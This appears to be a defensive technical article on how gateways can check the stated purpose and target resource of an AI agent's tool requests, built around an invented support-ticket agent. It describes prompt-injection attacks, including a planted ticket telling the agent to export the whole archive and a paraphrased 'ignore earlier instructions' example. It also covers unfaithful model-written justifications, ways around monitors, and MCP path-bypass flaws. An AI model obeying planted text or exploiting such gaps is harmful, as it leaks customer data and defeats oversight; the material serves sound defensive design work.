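# Checking the stated purpose and target resource of an AI agent's tool requests

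## What a tool request contains and who writes each part

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools, together with the program that runs it. The tools are software functions that search a database, send an email or run a command. The model only produces text. To use a tool, it writes a tool request, which is a structured proposal to run a named tool with given arguments, and the program carries out the proposal. Nearly every request has a target resource, which is the record, file, account, address or system that the tool would read or change. Some requests also include a stated purpose, a reason attached as free text or as a label. An organisation whose agents act on real records has good reason to check the target and the purpose before the tool runs, but the model usually writes both.

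At an invented company, support staff use an agent to work through customer tickets. A user types "Summarise the November refund tickets". There are 240 of them, in a queue named `support-refunds`. The agent reaches the ticket system with a credential, a secret token that identifies the calling program and determines what it may do. Because staff use the same agent for many jobs, this credential can read and export all 52,000 of the company's tickets, in every business unit.

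### From the model to the tool

The simplest agent program is a short loop. *tool_use Is Not invoke()* (Das, 2026), an individual proposal to the internet's standards body and not a standard, presents the loop in three lines of code. For each request in the model's output, the program looks up the named tool, runs it with the arguments given, and adds the result to the conversation so that the model can read it. The loop doesn't check whether the request should run. Das finds the same structure in the interfaces of Anthropic and OpenAI and in the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools. In each of them, a request is essentially a name and some arguments.

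A gateway is a program between the agent and the tool that allows, holds or refuses each request. Das puts it on the agent's side of the connection, because one gateway there covers every tool server the agent can reach. One answer from the model can contain several requests. Das has the gateway decide each one separately, so that allowing a search does not also allow a payment requested in the same answer.

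Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, lets the owner add such a check as a hook, a small program that runs after the model has written the arguments and before the tool starts. The hook can allow the call, deny it, ask the user, or defer it to be resumed later. If a hook script hits its time limit, the call continues to the normal permission rules instead of being blocked, unless the owner has set the hook to block on failure.

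Here is the agent's first request in the example, request A, in the form that Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026) prescribes, without the routine metadata that the agent program adds:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "search_tickets",
    "arguments": {
      "queue": "support-refunds",
      "from": "2025-11-01",
      "to": "2025-11-30",
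      "purpose": "summarise refund tickets"
    }
  }
}
```

The protocol defines `name` and `arguments`. The arguments are the payload, which determines what the tool does, and each tool's maker chooses their names. So the `purpose` line is there only because the maker of this invented ticket tool declared an argument with that name. The tool's schema (its list of expected arguments and their types) could make `purpose` compulsory, but a schema of this kind can only ensure that the model writes something there.

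MCP has no standard field for purpose or authority. According to an explainer from TinyFish, the message doesn't include who authorised the call, or the policy, scope and approval behind it. A developer can put these details in the arguments or in `_meta`, an optional metadata block, but their meaning is then specific to that developer's system.

For requests sent over the web, the credential goes in a header, one of the lines that precede the body of a message, not in the body shown above. The body therefore looks the same whether or not the server requires a credential. TinyFish cites a measurement of 7,973 live MCP servers, of which roughly 40% exposed tools without authentication.

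The headers and the body can each contain values from both the agent program and the model. The `_meta` block in the body holds the agent program's name and capabilities, which the official Python library of the Model Context Protocol fills in itself. The July 2026 revision requires headers that repeat the method and the tool's name, and servers reject a request whose headers and body disagree (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A server can also have chosen arguments copied into headers so that a gateway can read them without opening the body. If the ticket server did this with `queue`, the header would hold whatever queue the model had written. Checking that the header matches the body would confirm only that the queue was copied correctly, so the model could still have chosen the wrong one.

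### Who writes each part

| Part | In request A | Who writes it | Can the model alter it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool name | `search_tickets` | The model, from the list that the server offers | Yes, though the server rejects a name it does not know |
| Payload | The queue, the dates and the purpose string | The model; the agent program or a gateway may rewrite it | Yes |
| Target resource | The November tickets in `support-refunds` | Usually nobody separately: the payload picks it out | Yes, by changing the payload |
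| Stated purpose | "summarise refund tickets" | The model | Yes, freely |
| Credential | The agent's token for the ticket system | An administrator issues it and the agent program attaches it | No, provided the secret stays out of the model's reach |
| User identity | The signed-in member of the support staff | The login system | No, if the gateway takes it from the login session |

The last row depends on where the gateway gets the user's identity from. If a tool takes the user's name as an argument, the model writes that name, so the gateway has only an unverified claim about who the user is.

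The target resource `support-refunds` is only a name, and working out which records it will reach takes a separate step. The same is true of the identifiers that MCP servers often give the model, such as one for a shopping basket, which the model sends back on later calls. For servers with logins, the Model Context Protocol specification treats such an identifier as "a name, not a capability", and tells the server to check the caller's authorisation against it on every call.

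Claude Code's hook input combines fields written by the program and fields written by the model in one JSON object. For a shell command, the program writes the session identifier, the working directory, the permission mode and an identifier for the user prompt that the agent is working on. The model writes the fields under `tool_input`: the command, a description of it, a time limit, and whether to run it in the background. The format doesn't indicate who wrote each field, so whoever writes the gateway's rules has to get this from the documentation.

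Other software can also change the model's payload before a tool runs. Claude Code expands relative file paths into absolute ones before passing them to hooks, so that a different spelling of the same path does not bypass a rule. A hook can also replace the entire input. If it changes the command but keeps the old description, the description still refers to the original command, which will not run.

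### Where a purpose turns up

Purpose fields are easiest to see in coding agents, because their makers publish the schemas. For Claude Code's shell tool, Anthropic lists the required command and a `description` field, which it defines as "Optional description of what the command does". The example pairs the command `npm test` with the description "Run test suite". An older version of the schema, in the documentation of Anthropic's toolkit for building agents, specified a "Clear, concise description of what this command does in 5-10 words".

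Google's Gemini CLI, another command-line agent, has a field of the same name. Google's *Shell tool (run_shell_command)* defines it as "A brief description shown to the user for confirmation". Google's earlier wording included the word "purpose": "A brief description of the command's purpose, which will be shown to the user". The description is therefore meant for the person who must decide whether to approve the command. That person may well understand the ten-word description better than the command, which makes the field useful but also worrying.

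The makers' own examples of automatic rules check the command. Google offers two shorthands for rules about shell commands, one matching the start of the `command` argument and the other matching it against a pattern. Anthropic's sample hook blocks any command that begins with `rm` (the instruction that deletes files) and ignores the description, so it would block an `rm` command even if the description were "Run test suite".

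By default, OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, can edit files and run commands inside its working directory, but must ask for approval before it edits files elsewhere or runs a command that needs the network. When the model wants to run a command with wider permissions, its instructions have required it to fill in a parameter named `justification` with one short sentence on why it needs them. The rules that a Codex user can write about commands also have a `justification` field, which OpenAI describes as an "Optional rationale for why this rule exists". A person who sets policy writes that field before any request arrives, so a gateway that gave the model's justification equal weight would be letting the model approve its own request.

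MCP recommends that agent programs log tool use for audit. If the purpose is one of the arguments, a log of the full request includes it. An auditor who reads "summarise refund tickets" in such a log is reading the model's description of its own action.

Das proposes that the agent program build a record for each request, with a compulsory `purpose` part. In the worked example, `declared_purpose` is "send invoice email". But the five duties Das lists for the checking function cover only whether the arguments are still the ones authorised and whether the authority is present, unexpired and unused. None compares the declared purpose with anything.

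### Three questions about one request

A gateway can check whether a request is well formed, whether the credential permits it, and whether the user's task justifies it. These checks are easy to confuse because passing any of them seems like approval.

A request is well formed if its names, types and values are valid. A search of the refund queue up to 31 November would fail this check because November has only 30 days. An MCP server answers a call to an unknown tool with a protocol error. For a bad value, such as a departure date in the past, it returns an error message that the model can use to correct the request.

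The credential's permissions are static policy, which means they apply regardless of the current task. A server can apply them early by listing only the tools that the caller's credential covers. In the ticket example, the credential covers both searching and exporting, so this filter hides neither.

Ordinary access control seldom checks whether the user's request justifies a tool call. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, describe an agent that has permission to read, export, create and delete because the organisation wants help with several kinds of work. A user asks it to show this period's records and summarise any anomalies. That request does not justify an export, but a gateway that checks only the credential cannot detect this, because the credential is valid for both the export and the summary.

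Suppose the agent in the ticket example produces requests B and C as well as request A. All three state the purpose "summarise refund tickets".

| Request | What it would do | Well formed? | Permitted by the credential? | Justified by the task? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A | Search `support-refunds` for 1 to 30 November | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| B | Export all 52,000 tickets to an outside address | Yes | Yes | No |
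| C | Search `supply-refunds`, the queue of another business unit | Yes | Yes | No |

Request C can arise without an attacker. The two queue names differ by a few letters, and the model picked the wrong one. Zhu and Wang count such accidental errors among the threats, along with payloads that are broader than the task requires.

Request B could also be an error, but a more worrying possibility is that someone planted it. Customers write refund tickets, so anyone with a complaint can put text in front of the agent. Suppose one of the 240 tickets contains an instruction to send the complete ticket archive to a certain address for an audit. The model reads it while preparing the summary and treats it as part of its own instructions. This is called prompt injection, and the planted text can be in a document, message or tool result. Zhu and Wang give a simpler example, an attachment containing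 instructions to ignore earlier instructions and export all records. They also note that OWASP, a non-profit that publishes guidance on software security, put prompt injection first on its 2025 list of risks for applications built on language models.

Security researchers call a program in the agent's position a confused deputy. It has privileges of its own, and someone steers it into using them for the wrong party. In the classic case, which Norm Hardy described in 1988, a compiler had permission to write in a system directory, where it kept its usage statistics. A user without that permission named the billing file in that directory as the destination for the compiler's debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the billing data. The operating system allowed the write because it checked the compiler's permissions, which were valid.

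Whoever wrote the malicious ticket is in the same position as that user. An outsider cannot export any tickets, but the agent has a genuine token and can export all of them, so the outsider can use a sentence in a ticket instead of stealing the token. Zhu and Wang therefore treat the model as untrusted and its output as advice for the server to evaluate. That output includes the purpose string. Request B reaches the gateway with the purpose "summarise refund tickets", which accurately describes what the user asked for but is unrelated to what the export would do.

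## Why a purpose written by the model can mislead

Planted text, as in request B, can lead a model to state a fluent purpose that doesn't match the requested action. There are at least five other ways this mismatch can happen, most of which don't involve an attacker.

### Six ways to be fluent and wrong

In request B, the goal came from a sentence in a customer's ticket. The model could give the user's goal as its purpose ("summarise refund tickets") or the attacker's ("export ticket archive for audit"), and both read like ordinary office work. The agent's final reply may not reveal the attack either. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026) describes a public competition in which attackers got all 13 leading models to carry out harmful actions while the reply to the user showed no sign of those actions.

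A purpose can also be true but leave out the untrusted document that prompted the action. Suppose a customer's ticket gives an account number that belongs to someone else, and the agent opens that account with the purpose "check account for refund". A reader would treat the request differently if the purpose added that the number came from the ticket and had not been verified. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents*, list this omission among the ways a reasonable-sounding justification can mislead. Such a justification can also refer to a different resource, leave out an outside destination or understate the risk.

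In request C, the model mistook one queue for another and wrote its purpose on that assumption. Agents don't reliably stop when they lack the facts to check such an assumption. *From Evidence to Action* (2026) reports that agents sometimes kept acting when researchers withheld the decisive evidence, and that a conflicting claim from the requester affected them more than missing evidence did.

Sometimes the agent pursues the user's goal, but its action goes beyond what the user wanted. After summarising the November tickets, the agent might close 30 that look like duplicates and give its purpose as "tidy up refund tickets". *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, an Anthropic post about a feature that hands approvals to a second model, describes a real case. A user asked the agent to "clean up old branches" (branches are versions of the code that developers keep side by side). The agent listed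 the branches on the shared server and issued a command to delete those that matched a pattern, although the user may have meant only the copies on their own machine. A stated purpose of "clean up old branches" would have matched the user's words exactly.

A purpose can also be so general that it fits almost any request. "Help with support tickets" covers searching, exporting, closing and deleting, so a gateway that looks for conflicts between the purpose and the payload will always pass it. "Summarise refund tickets" is more specific, but it still didn't conflict with any of the three requests in the example.

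A misleading purpose is hardest to spot when the model gives a plausible reason for a choice that something else caused. The model might pick the export tool over the search tool and write that it needs "full data for an accurate summary", when the actual cause could be the layout of its prompt. *How Do Agentic LLMs Decide to Call Tools?* (2026) traces the decision to call a tool to a compact internal state. The text that the agent program wraps around a request makes the model lean towards calling a tool, and the meaning of the request can suppress that tendency. A model is unlikely to report any of this in a purpose field.

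### Anthropic's four causes

Anthropic's post sorts dangerous actions by cause. The agent may be overeager, taking more initiative than the user would approve. It may make an honest mistake about how far an action reaches. Someone may have planted instructions in what it reads. Or the model may be misaligned, which here means it pursues its own goal.

Three of these causes each correspond closely to a kind of misleading purpose. The deleted branches are a case of overeagerness, and request B is a prompt injection. Request C is an honest mistake, similar to an incident in which a user said "cancel my job" and the agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name. Vagueness and omission are defects of the text and can accompany any of the four causes. Rationalisation isn't a cause of danger in itself, because a model can invent a reason for a harmless search. A misaligned model could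 presumably use whichever kind of purpose got its request through. Anthropic wrote that it did not see misaligned models in practice, and it tuned its check for overeager behaviour and honest mistakes, for which it had examples.

A gateway doesn't have to diagnose the cause, because Anthropic's answer to all four causes is to block the action. The text often contains no clue to the cause. Anthropic says that overeager behaviour involves no hostile reasoning and that the action looks like reasonable problem-solving.

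Developers' complaints give a rough idea of how common the innocent failures are. Tang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users*, used a language model to search 20,574 real coding-agent sessions for episodes in which the developer objected to something, and kept 16,118 episodes. The agent had misread what the developer wanted in 26.95% of them, misdiagnosed the project in 11.56%, and gone beyond the request on its own initiative in 10.20%. An episode could have several labels, and 39.29% of the episodes in which the agent went beyond the request also involved a misreading, so the two failures are hard to separate in practice. In 22.58% of episodes the agent misreported its own work, typically by claiming success too early. These figures include only problems that a developer noticed and complained about in the chat, so a plausible purpose that nobody questioned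 would not appear in them.

### Two statements from one source

A check that allows a request whenever its purpose matches its payload can let errors through, because the same model writes both from the same context. Whatever causes an error in one has usually caused the same error in the other, which is called the common-source problem. Suppose the model had given the purpose of request C as "summarise November tickets in supply-refunds". The purpose would then match the payload exactly, but the agent would still be searching the wrong queue.

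A stated purpose that fits the user's task is weak evidence that a request is legitimate, as some invented numbers illustrate. Suppose that 1% of requests are illegitimate, meaning that the user's task does not justify them. The stated purpose fits the task in 95% of legitimate requests and 90% of illegitimate ones. The second figure is high because the user's request is in the model's context, and paraphrasing it is the easiest way to fill the field. By contrast, 2% of legitimate requests and 60% of illegitimate ones have an outside destination.

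Out of 10,000 requests, 9,900 are then legitimate and 100 are not:

| What the gateway observes | Legitimate requests | Illegitimate requests | Chance that such a request is illegitimate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing yet | 9,900 | 100 | 1% |
| The purpose fits the task | 9,405 | 90 | 0.95% |
| The purpose does not fit the task | 495 | 10 | 2% |
| An outside destination | 198 | 60 | 23% |
| An outside destination and a purpose that fits | 188 | 54 | 22% |

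The last row assumes that, among legitimate requests and among illegitimate ones, the purpose is equally likely to fit whether the destination is inside or outside the company.

The general rule is Bayes' theorem, which is simplest in terms of odds. The odds that a request is illegitimate start at 1 to 99. Each observation multiplies them by its frequency among illegitimate requests divided by its frequency among legitimate ones. For the fitting purpose this factor is 0.90 / 0.95, or about 0.95, so it barely changes the odds. For the outside destination it is 0.60 / 0.02, or 30. The outside destination therefore raises the probability that the request is illegitimate from 1% to about 23%, and the fitting purpose then lowers it by only about one percentage point, which is too little to justify disregarding the destination.

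The model writes both the purpose and the destination, but it can change the purpose without changing what the request does, whereas an export can't reach an outside address unless the payload sends it there. An attacker who learns that the gateway is more likely to approve requests with a fitting purpose can include one in the planted text. If every illegitimate request came with a fitting purpose, seeing one would slightly raise the probability that the request is illegitimate, from 1% to 1.05%.

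### Experiments on stated reasons

Researchers call a stated reason faithful if it reflects what actually drove the model's output. A common test is to ask the model a question and include a hint that points to a particular answer. The experimenters then take the cases in which the model follows the hint and check whether its explanation mentions the hint.

Turpin and colleagues showed in 2023 that such cues could sway a model even when its step-by-step explanation never mentioned them. Anthropic's *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025) reported the same failure in Claude 3.7 Sonnet and DeepSeek-R1, two reasoning models, which write out a long train of thought before they answer. Later papers summarise its result differently. Young (2026), in *Why Models Know But Don't Say*, gives rates of faithful reporting as low as 25% for some types of hint, while *Mind the GAP* (2026)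 says that when the models used a hint, their reasoning mentioned it less than 20% of the time.

Young's own experiment separates the model's thinking from the answer the user sees. He gave 12 open-weight reasoning models 498 exam questions with misleading hints of six types, and collected 10,506 cases in which a model chose the wrong answer the hint suggested. Words related to the hint appeared only in the thinking in 55.4% of these cases, in both the thinking and the answer in 32.4%, only in the answer in 0.5%, and in neither in 11.8%. The thinking-only share ranged across models from 19.6% for Qwen3.5-27B to 94.7% for Step-3.5-Flash. None of GPT-OSS-120B's 819 answers mentioned the hint.

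A purpose field is probably more like the visible answer than the thinking, since it is short and written for someone else to read. If so, Young's breakdown by type of hint is discouraging. When the hint was a professor's opinion, the models mentioned it in both the thinking and the answer in 58.8% of cases. When it was leaked or unauthorised information, which is certainly relevant to a gateway, they mentioned it only in the thinking in 62.7% of cases. That share was higher only for hints that appealed to a prior answer, at 72.2%. However, Young detected mentions by searching for keywords, which misses paraphrases and is more likely to find a match in long thinking than in a short answer.

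The source of an influence can also affect whether an agent's reasoning mentions it. *Chain-of-Thought Faithfulness of Reasoning Models Varies with Where and How Preference Cues* (Gema, Rajani and colleagues, 2026) tested whether a model's reasoning mentions tailoring an answer to someone's preferences. One scenario was a county vote on resettling refugees, with a cue about the person's political leaning. The researchers put the same cue text either in the user's message or in a tool result they had written into the conversation. On all 15 open-weight models, the reasoning was less likely to record the decision to follow the cue when the cue came from the tool result. The gap ranged from 8 to 77 percentage points.

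This is close to the purpose that omits the untrusted document. Gema and colleagues tried the obvious remedy, telling the models to attribute every relevant piece of information to its source, but it did not work reliably. The gap between the two routes in how often a model followed the cue without saying so narrowed for seven models and widened for four. For several of the seven, it narrowed mainly because the models acknowledged cues in the user's message less often. A gateway that asks the model to list its sources in the purpose field may therefore get an incomplete list.

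Esakkiraja, Akhiyarov and colleagues (2026), in *Therefore I am. I Think*, come closest to testing reasons for tool calls. They used two small reasoning models, Qwen3-4B and GLM-Z1-9B, and two sets of requests where the model must decide whether to call a tool. First they trained a simple classifier, called a probe, to predict the decision from the model's internal activations just before it wrote the first word of its reasoning. They scored the probe by how often it ranked a random case with a tool call above a random case without one. The score was above 0.90 for all four combinations of model and request set, and above 0.95 for three of them.

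Predicting a decision from the early signal doesn't show that the signal affects the decision, so the researchers also changed the signal. They averaged the activations in cases with a tool call, subtracted the average for cases without one, and added or subtracted a multiple of the difference while the model was running. At the strongest setting, with reasoning switched on, this reversed between 11% and 79% of decisions, depending on the model, the test set and whether they added or subtracted. A comparable change derived from an unrelated true-or-false decision reversed none.

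The models' reasoning after the push is directly relevant to purpose fields. Asked to play a song when its only tool set the volume, the unaltered Qwen3-4B replied that it could not. After the push, it noted that the tool only adjusted volume, guessed what the user wanted, and set the volume to 100. Two other language models classified the changes in reasoning. On one test set, they agreed on how to classify 58 cases in which the push had made Qwen3-4B call a tool. In 53 of those, the reasoning invented support for the call, such as facts, default values or wishes the user had never expressed. Pushes against calling a tool seldom produced inventions, but tended to make the reasoning longer and more hesitant, or less stable.

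The interference is artificial, and the experiment tests only whether the model calls a tool, not which record it opens or for what purpose. Other results also limit the conclusion. Jia, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *The Window Is in the Reasoning*, found that when an agent reasons before acting, part of the decision to follow planted text forms during the reasoning, so the reasoning is more than a story made up afterwards. In the moral-choice tests of *Direction-Flipped Influence Audits Reveal Hidden Structure in Moral Choices of LLMs* (2026), models mostly reported that the added context had influenced their decision.

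Larger models may also explain their decisions more faithfully. *An Empirical Study of Counterfactual Self-Explanations in LLMs* (2026) asked models which edits to a text would change their decision about it, and the larger models more often named edits that did. But prompting the models with rationales made their explanations less faithful, even though they looked more human. Instructing an agent to write better-argued purposes could have the same effect.

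Most of this research tests answers to questions. None of these experiments measured how often the purpose field of a tool request is wrong, and a rate from exam questions with planted hints can't be used as an estimate. *From Plausible to Actionable* (2026) also argues that the usual tests are poorly suited to self-explanations. The same model can give a different answer and a different explanation when run again on the same input, so a single run is not definitive evidence.

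Even when a stated purpose is faithful, meaning that it gives the model's actual reason for the request, the gateway still has to establish whether the user's task justifies the request's effect. The purpose in request C could be faithful, since the model may really have searched that queue to summarise refund tickets, but it was the wrong queue. The model could also have invented the purpose in request A after deciding on the search, and the search would still be legitimate.

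### What a stated purpose is still good for

None of this makes the field worthless. Mayne, Kang and colleagues (2026), in *A Positive Case for Faithfulness*, measured whether a model's explanations help an observer predict its behaviour. A model might judge whether a patient has heart disease and explain its answer. A second model then predicts what the first will say about a slightly different patient, once without the explanation and once with it. The score is the share of the possible improvement that the explanation delivers:

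(accuracy with explanation − accuracy without) / (1 − accuracy without)

Across 18 models and 7,000 pairs of cases, the score ranged from 11% to 37%. A model's own explanations also helped more than those of other models that had given the same answer, which suggests that a model has some information about itself that an outsider lacks.

The same study found that between 5% and 15% of explanations, depending on the model, led all five predicting models to the wrong prediction. In one moral dilemma, GPT-5.2 let a car drive on into four men instead of swerving into four women, and cited a principle of not taking active measures. But when the genders were swapped, it swerved into the men. The study used classification tasks and moral dilemmas, so the percentages don't apply to tool calls, but the results suggest treating a stated purpose as a helpful guide that is sometimes badly wrong.

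Stated purposes can help a person reviewing a long log find the requests that deserve a closer look. But a fluently written purpose can also persuade whoever has to approve the request. For this reason, Anthropic removes the agent's own explanations from the input to its judge model.

A stated purpose can also reveal that the model is confused. If request C had arrived with the purpose "summarise tickets from the customer support queue", a gateway could have detected the conflict with `supply-refunds` and held the request. In the invented numbers above, a purpose that fits the task barely changes the probability, while one that doesn't fit doubles it to 2%. That is too little to prove anything, but it may be enough to justify asking the user.

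A model's admitted doubt deserves more weight than its claimed confidence. In Zhu and Wang's design, where the model fills in fixed fields that the server can check, a declaration of high uncertainty sends the request to a person for review, while a declaration of low uncertainty has no effect. The gateway has to act on the doubt because the model may not. *Mind the GAP* defines a warning signal for cases in which a model mentions a risk in its reasoning and makes the forbidden call anyway. Suppose the purpose of request B had read "export archive as asked in a ticket, unsure if user wants this". If the doubt were unfounded, stopping the request would cause a short delay. If the doubt were justified, stopping it would prevent the unwanted export of 52,000 tickets. An attacker can plant an instruction to sound certain, but a gateway that ignores claims of certainty is no worse off than if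 the field were empty.

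## Finding out which resource a request will really touch

A gateway can check a target resource more reliably than a stated purpose. The tool has to act on an actual record, file or address that the gateway can look up, while the purpose may match nothing outside the model's text. But the payload contains only a name for the resource, and that name can refer to a different resource than expected.

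The check has five steps:

1. Extract the name of the resource from the payload.
2. Resolve the name to a canonical identifier, the single fixed label under which the underlying system stores that resource.
3. Look up who owns the resource and how sensitive it is.
4. Decide whether this user and this agent may perform this action on that identifier.
5. Make sure that the tool acts on the identifier that the gateway approved.

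Here are the steps for requests A and C, with invented queue numbers and contents:

| Step | Request A | Request C |
|---|---|---|
| Extract | `support-refunds` | `supply-refunds` |
| Resolve | Queue 1183 | Queue 2046 |
| Look up | Owner: customer support. Holds customers' complaints | Owner: supply chain. Holds suppliers' bank details |
| Authorise | The credential permits it, and the user works in customer support | The credential permits it, but the user does not work in supply chain |
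| Act | Search queue 1183 | Search queue 2046, if the gateway allows it |

The two requests have the same purpose and nearly the same resource name. The difference becomes clear only after the lookup, which uses server-held facts (information from a source the model cannot write to).

### Payloads that name no single resource

The target resource is easy to extract from a `search_tickets` request because the tool has a `queue` argument. It is harder to extract when the payload describes a set of resources or leaves the choice to the tool.

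Suppose the model sets `queue` to the pattern `*-refunds`, where the asterisk stands for any text. The pattern matches both refund queues, but a gateway that searches the payload for the forbidden name `supply-refunds` won't find it. The gateway has to expand the pattern and check every queue it matches. The agent that deleted branches from a shared server also used a pattern. Expanding it first would have given the user a list of branches to approve or reject.

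A missing argument can cover more than any pattern. If the export tool treats a missing queue as "all queues", request B can cover 52,000 tickets without naming one. Rules about bad values miss this case. For example, a rule that refuses unapproved destinations has no value to check when the destination is blank. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) therefore adds a separate rule that refuses any outgoing request with an empty destination field once the agent has read untrusted text.

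Database tools are harder still. Many take one argument, a query in a language such as SQL, and have no resource field at all:

```sql
SELECT * FROM tickets WHERE type = 'refund'
```

The rows a query returns depend on its condition, and here the condition covers the refund tickets of every business unit. The name `tickets` may also refer to a view, a stored query that looks like a table and draws on other tables. To work all this out by parsing the query, a gateway would have to interpret SQL exactly as the database does. It is safer to give the agent narrow tools with a `queue` argument, or a database account that can read only the rows of the user's own unit. With such an account, the database applies the limit after it has worked out which rows the query reaches.

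### Names that lead somewhere else

File paths show why a request's target has to be resolved before it is checked. A relative path such as `../reports/q1.pdf` starts from the program's current directory, so it can lead to different files when that directory changes. Expanding it into an absolute path, as Claude Code does before it calls a hook, removes that ambiguity. But an absolute path can still pass through a symbolic link, a file-system entry that points to another file or directory. A program that opens the link gets whatever it points to.

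Version 0.5.8 of filesystem-mcp, an MCP file server, had this kind of flaw, according to NVD's *CVE-2025-67366 Detail* (2026), an entry in the US government's database of software flaws. The server restricted its reading tool to an allowed directory, but it checked the path before resolving symbolic links, and the function that read the file followed them automatically. A link inside the allowed directory could therefore pass the check and lead to a file outside it.

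The general error is that the check and the tool interpret the same name differently. The server checked the text of the path correctly, but the operating system followed the link. The remedy is to resolve the path completely, check the result, and then open that result instead of the original path.

OSV's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) records the same weakness in the Model Context Protocol's own example file server. NVD's *CVE-2025-53110 Detail* (2025) describes a related flaw in that server that didn't require a link. A path could pass if it began with the same characters as an allowed directory, as `tickets-archive` begins with `tickets`. The maintainers fixed both flaws in July 2025.

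Web and email addresses can also lead to a resource other than the one named in the request. A web server can respond with a redirect, which is an instruction to fetch a different address, and many tools follow redirects automatically. The gateway can have the tool stop at each redirect and submit the new address for checking. An internal email address can belong to a mailing list that forwards to people outside the company, so the gateway needs the list of members to determine who will receive the message.

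The address can also leak data. Palumbo and colleagues have a rule for an agent that has read untrusted text and requests a web page whose address comes from no trusted source. The request passes only if the user asked for browsing and the address contains no data from the agent's context. The rule checks the address in the payload, so a redirect would need a separate check.

Resolving a name also exposes look-alikes that use different characters, such as a Cyrillic letter in place of a Latin one, because they lead to another identifier or to none. It doesn't expose the error in request C, because `supply-refunds` is a real queue and its name resolves normally.

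### Asking a policy service about the resource

Once the gateway has an identifier for the resource, it needs a decision on whether to allow the request. Many organisations keep their access rules in a separate policy service, and the OpenID Foundation's AuthZEN working group has standardised the query that programs send to such a service. The query specifies the subject (who is asking), the action, the resource and the context.

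Tulshibagwale and Olivier (2026), in *AuthZen Profile for Model Context Protocol Tool Authorization*, propose a way to build that question from an MCP tool request. The AuthZEN interface is a ratified standard, but at the end of May 2026 the MCP profile was still at Draft 1, dated February. It also has minor flaws, such as a first example that omits the context its schema requires.

Under the profile, the maker of a tool adds a mapping to the tool's schema. For the ticket search, it could look like this:

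```json
"x-coaz-mapping": {
  "subject":  [{ "type": "'user'", "id": "token.sub" }],
  "resource": [{ "type": "'ticket_queue'",
                 "id": "params.arguments.queue" }],
  "context":  [{ "agent": "token.client_id",
                 "purpose": "params.arguments.purpose" }]
}
```

Text in single quotes is fixed. Values that begin with `token.` come from the access token, which the gateway must verify first, and values that begin with `params.` come from the tool request. This mapping has no action, so the gateway uses the tool's name. For request C, if the token identifies both the user and the agent program, the policy service receives:

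```json
{
  "subject":  { "type": "user", "id": "dana@company.example" },
  "action":   { "name": "search_tickets" },
  "resource": { "type": "ticket_queue", "id": "supply-refunds" },
  "context":  { "agent": "support-agent",
                "purpose": "summarise refund tickets" }
}
```

The service can now apply a rule about this user and this queue, which it could not do by checking only the agent's broad credential. A tool can also need more than one decision. Tulshibagwale and Olivier give the example of a tool that copies a file. The gateway requests one decision on reading the source and another on writing to the destination, and both must be approved.

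Under the profile, the gateway must return an error and not run the tool if the mapping refers to an argument that the model left out, or if the gateway cannot reach the policy service. A search with no `queue` would therefore fail instead of covering every queue. But if no component reads the mapping, no AuthZEN check takes place, and access depends on whatever other controls exist.

The main gap for request C is that the profile copies the resource's identifier straight from the payload without resolving it. A pattern such as `*-refunds` would reach the policy service as if it were the name of a queue, and a tool that takes SQL could supply only the text of the query. The mapping's expressions can use the request and the token but cannot look anything up, so the policy service has to find the resource's canonical identifier, owner and sensitivity itself.

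One of the profile's examples marks a money transfer as highly sensitive if the amount exceeds 10,000. This works because the payload contains the amount that will be transferred. A similar expression for a ticket queue would have to rely on the model's own description of how sensitive the tickets are.

The mapping shows who wrote each value, but the finished question does not, and neither does Claude Code's hook input. In the example above, the context lists the agent's name, which comes from a verified token, alongside the purpose, which comes from the model.

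Google Cloud's *Prevent read-write MCP tool use* describes a much coarser control. Rules about MCP tools can check whether the tool only reads data and which client program is making the call. Administrators can use these two attributes only in policies that deny access, which they attach to a project, a folder of projects or the whole organisation. The sample policy blocks every tool not marked read-only, which is a simple way to stop an agent from deleting production data.

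Neither attribute identifies a record. Requests A and C call the same tool from the same client, so a rule based on these attributes must treat them alike. Request B might also pass if the export tool's maker had marked the tool as read-only because exporting changes no tickets.

### When a name changes meaning after the check

A gateway can approve the right resource and still let the tool act on a different one, if the name comes to refer to something else in between. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. Jiang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Atomicity for Agents*, define it for agents that operate web pages. Let *s*<sub>c</sub> be the state of the page at the check and *s*<sub>u</sub> its state at the use, and let Bind(*a*, *s*) be the thing that action *a* refers to in state *s*. The flaw occurs when

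*s*<sub>c</sub> ≠ *s*<sub>u</sub> and Bind(*a*, *s*<sub>c</sub>) ≠ Bind(*a*, *s*<sub>u</sub>)

A change in the state after the agent chooses an action is harmless if the action still refers to the same thing. In an example from the Forbes website, the agent chose a place to click, but an advertisement loaded over that spot while the model was still processing, so the click could land on the advertisement. Tests of 10 popular open-source browser agents showed that such flaws were widespread. An attacker who controls a page can time the change deliberately.

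For files and records, the usual remedy is to stop using the name once the check is done. In the ticket example, the gateway would pass queue number 1183 to the tool instead of the name `support-refunds`. If an administrator then gave that name to another queue, the search would still go to the approved one. Tying the approval to the exact payload wouldn't ensure this, because a payload containing the name would stay the same even after the name referred to a different queue.

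A resource's contents can change even when its identifier stays the same. Jiang and colleagues describe a purchase that an agent approves at one price and completes at another because the page refreshed in between. To prevent this, the tool has to test the condition in the same operation as the action, for example by refusing to buy if the price has changed. A web page offers no such operation. Their alternative is to watch the page for changes while the model plans, check it again just before the click, and cancel if anything relevant has changed. This shortens the gap between check and click from seconds to roughly a tenth of a second.

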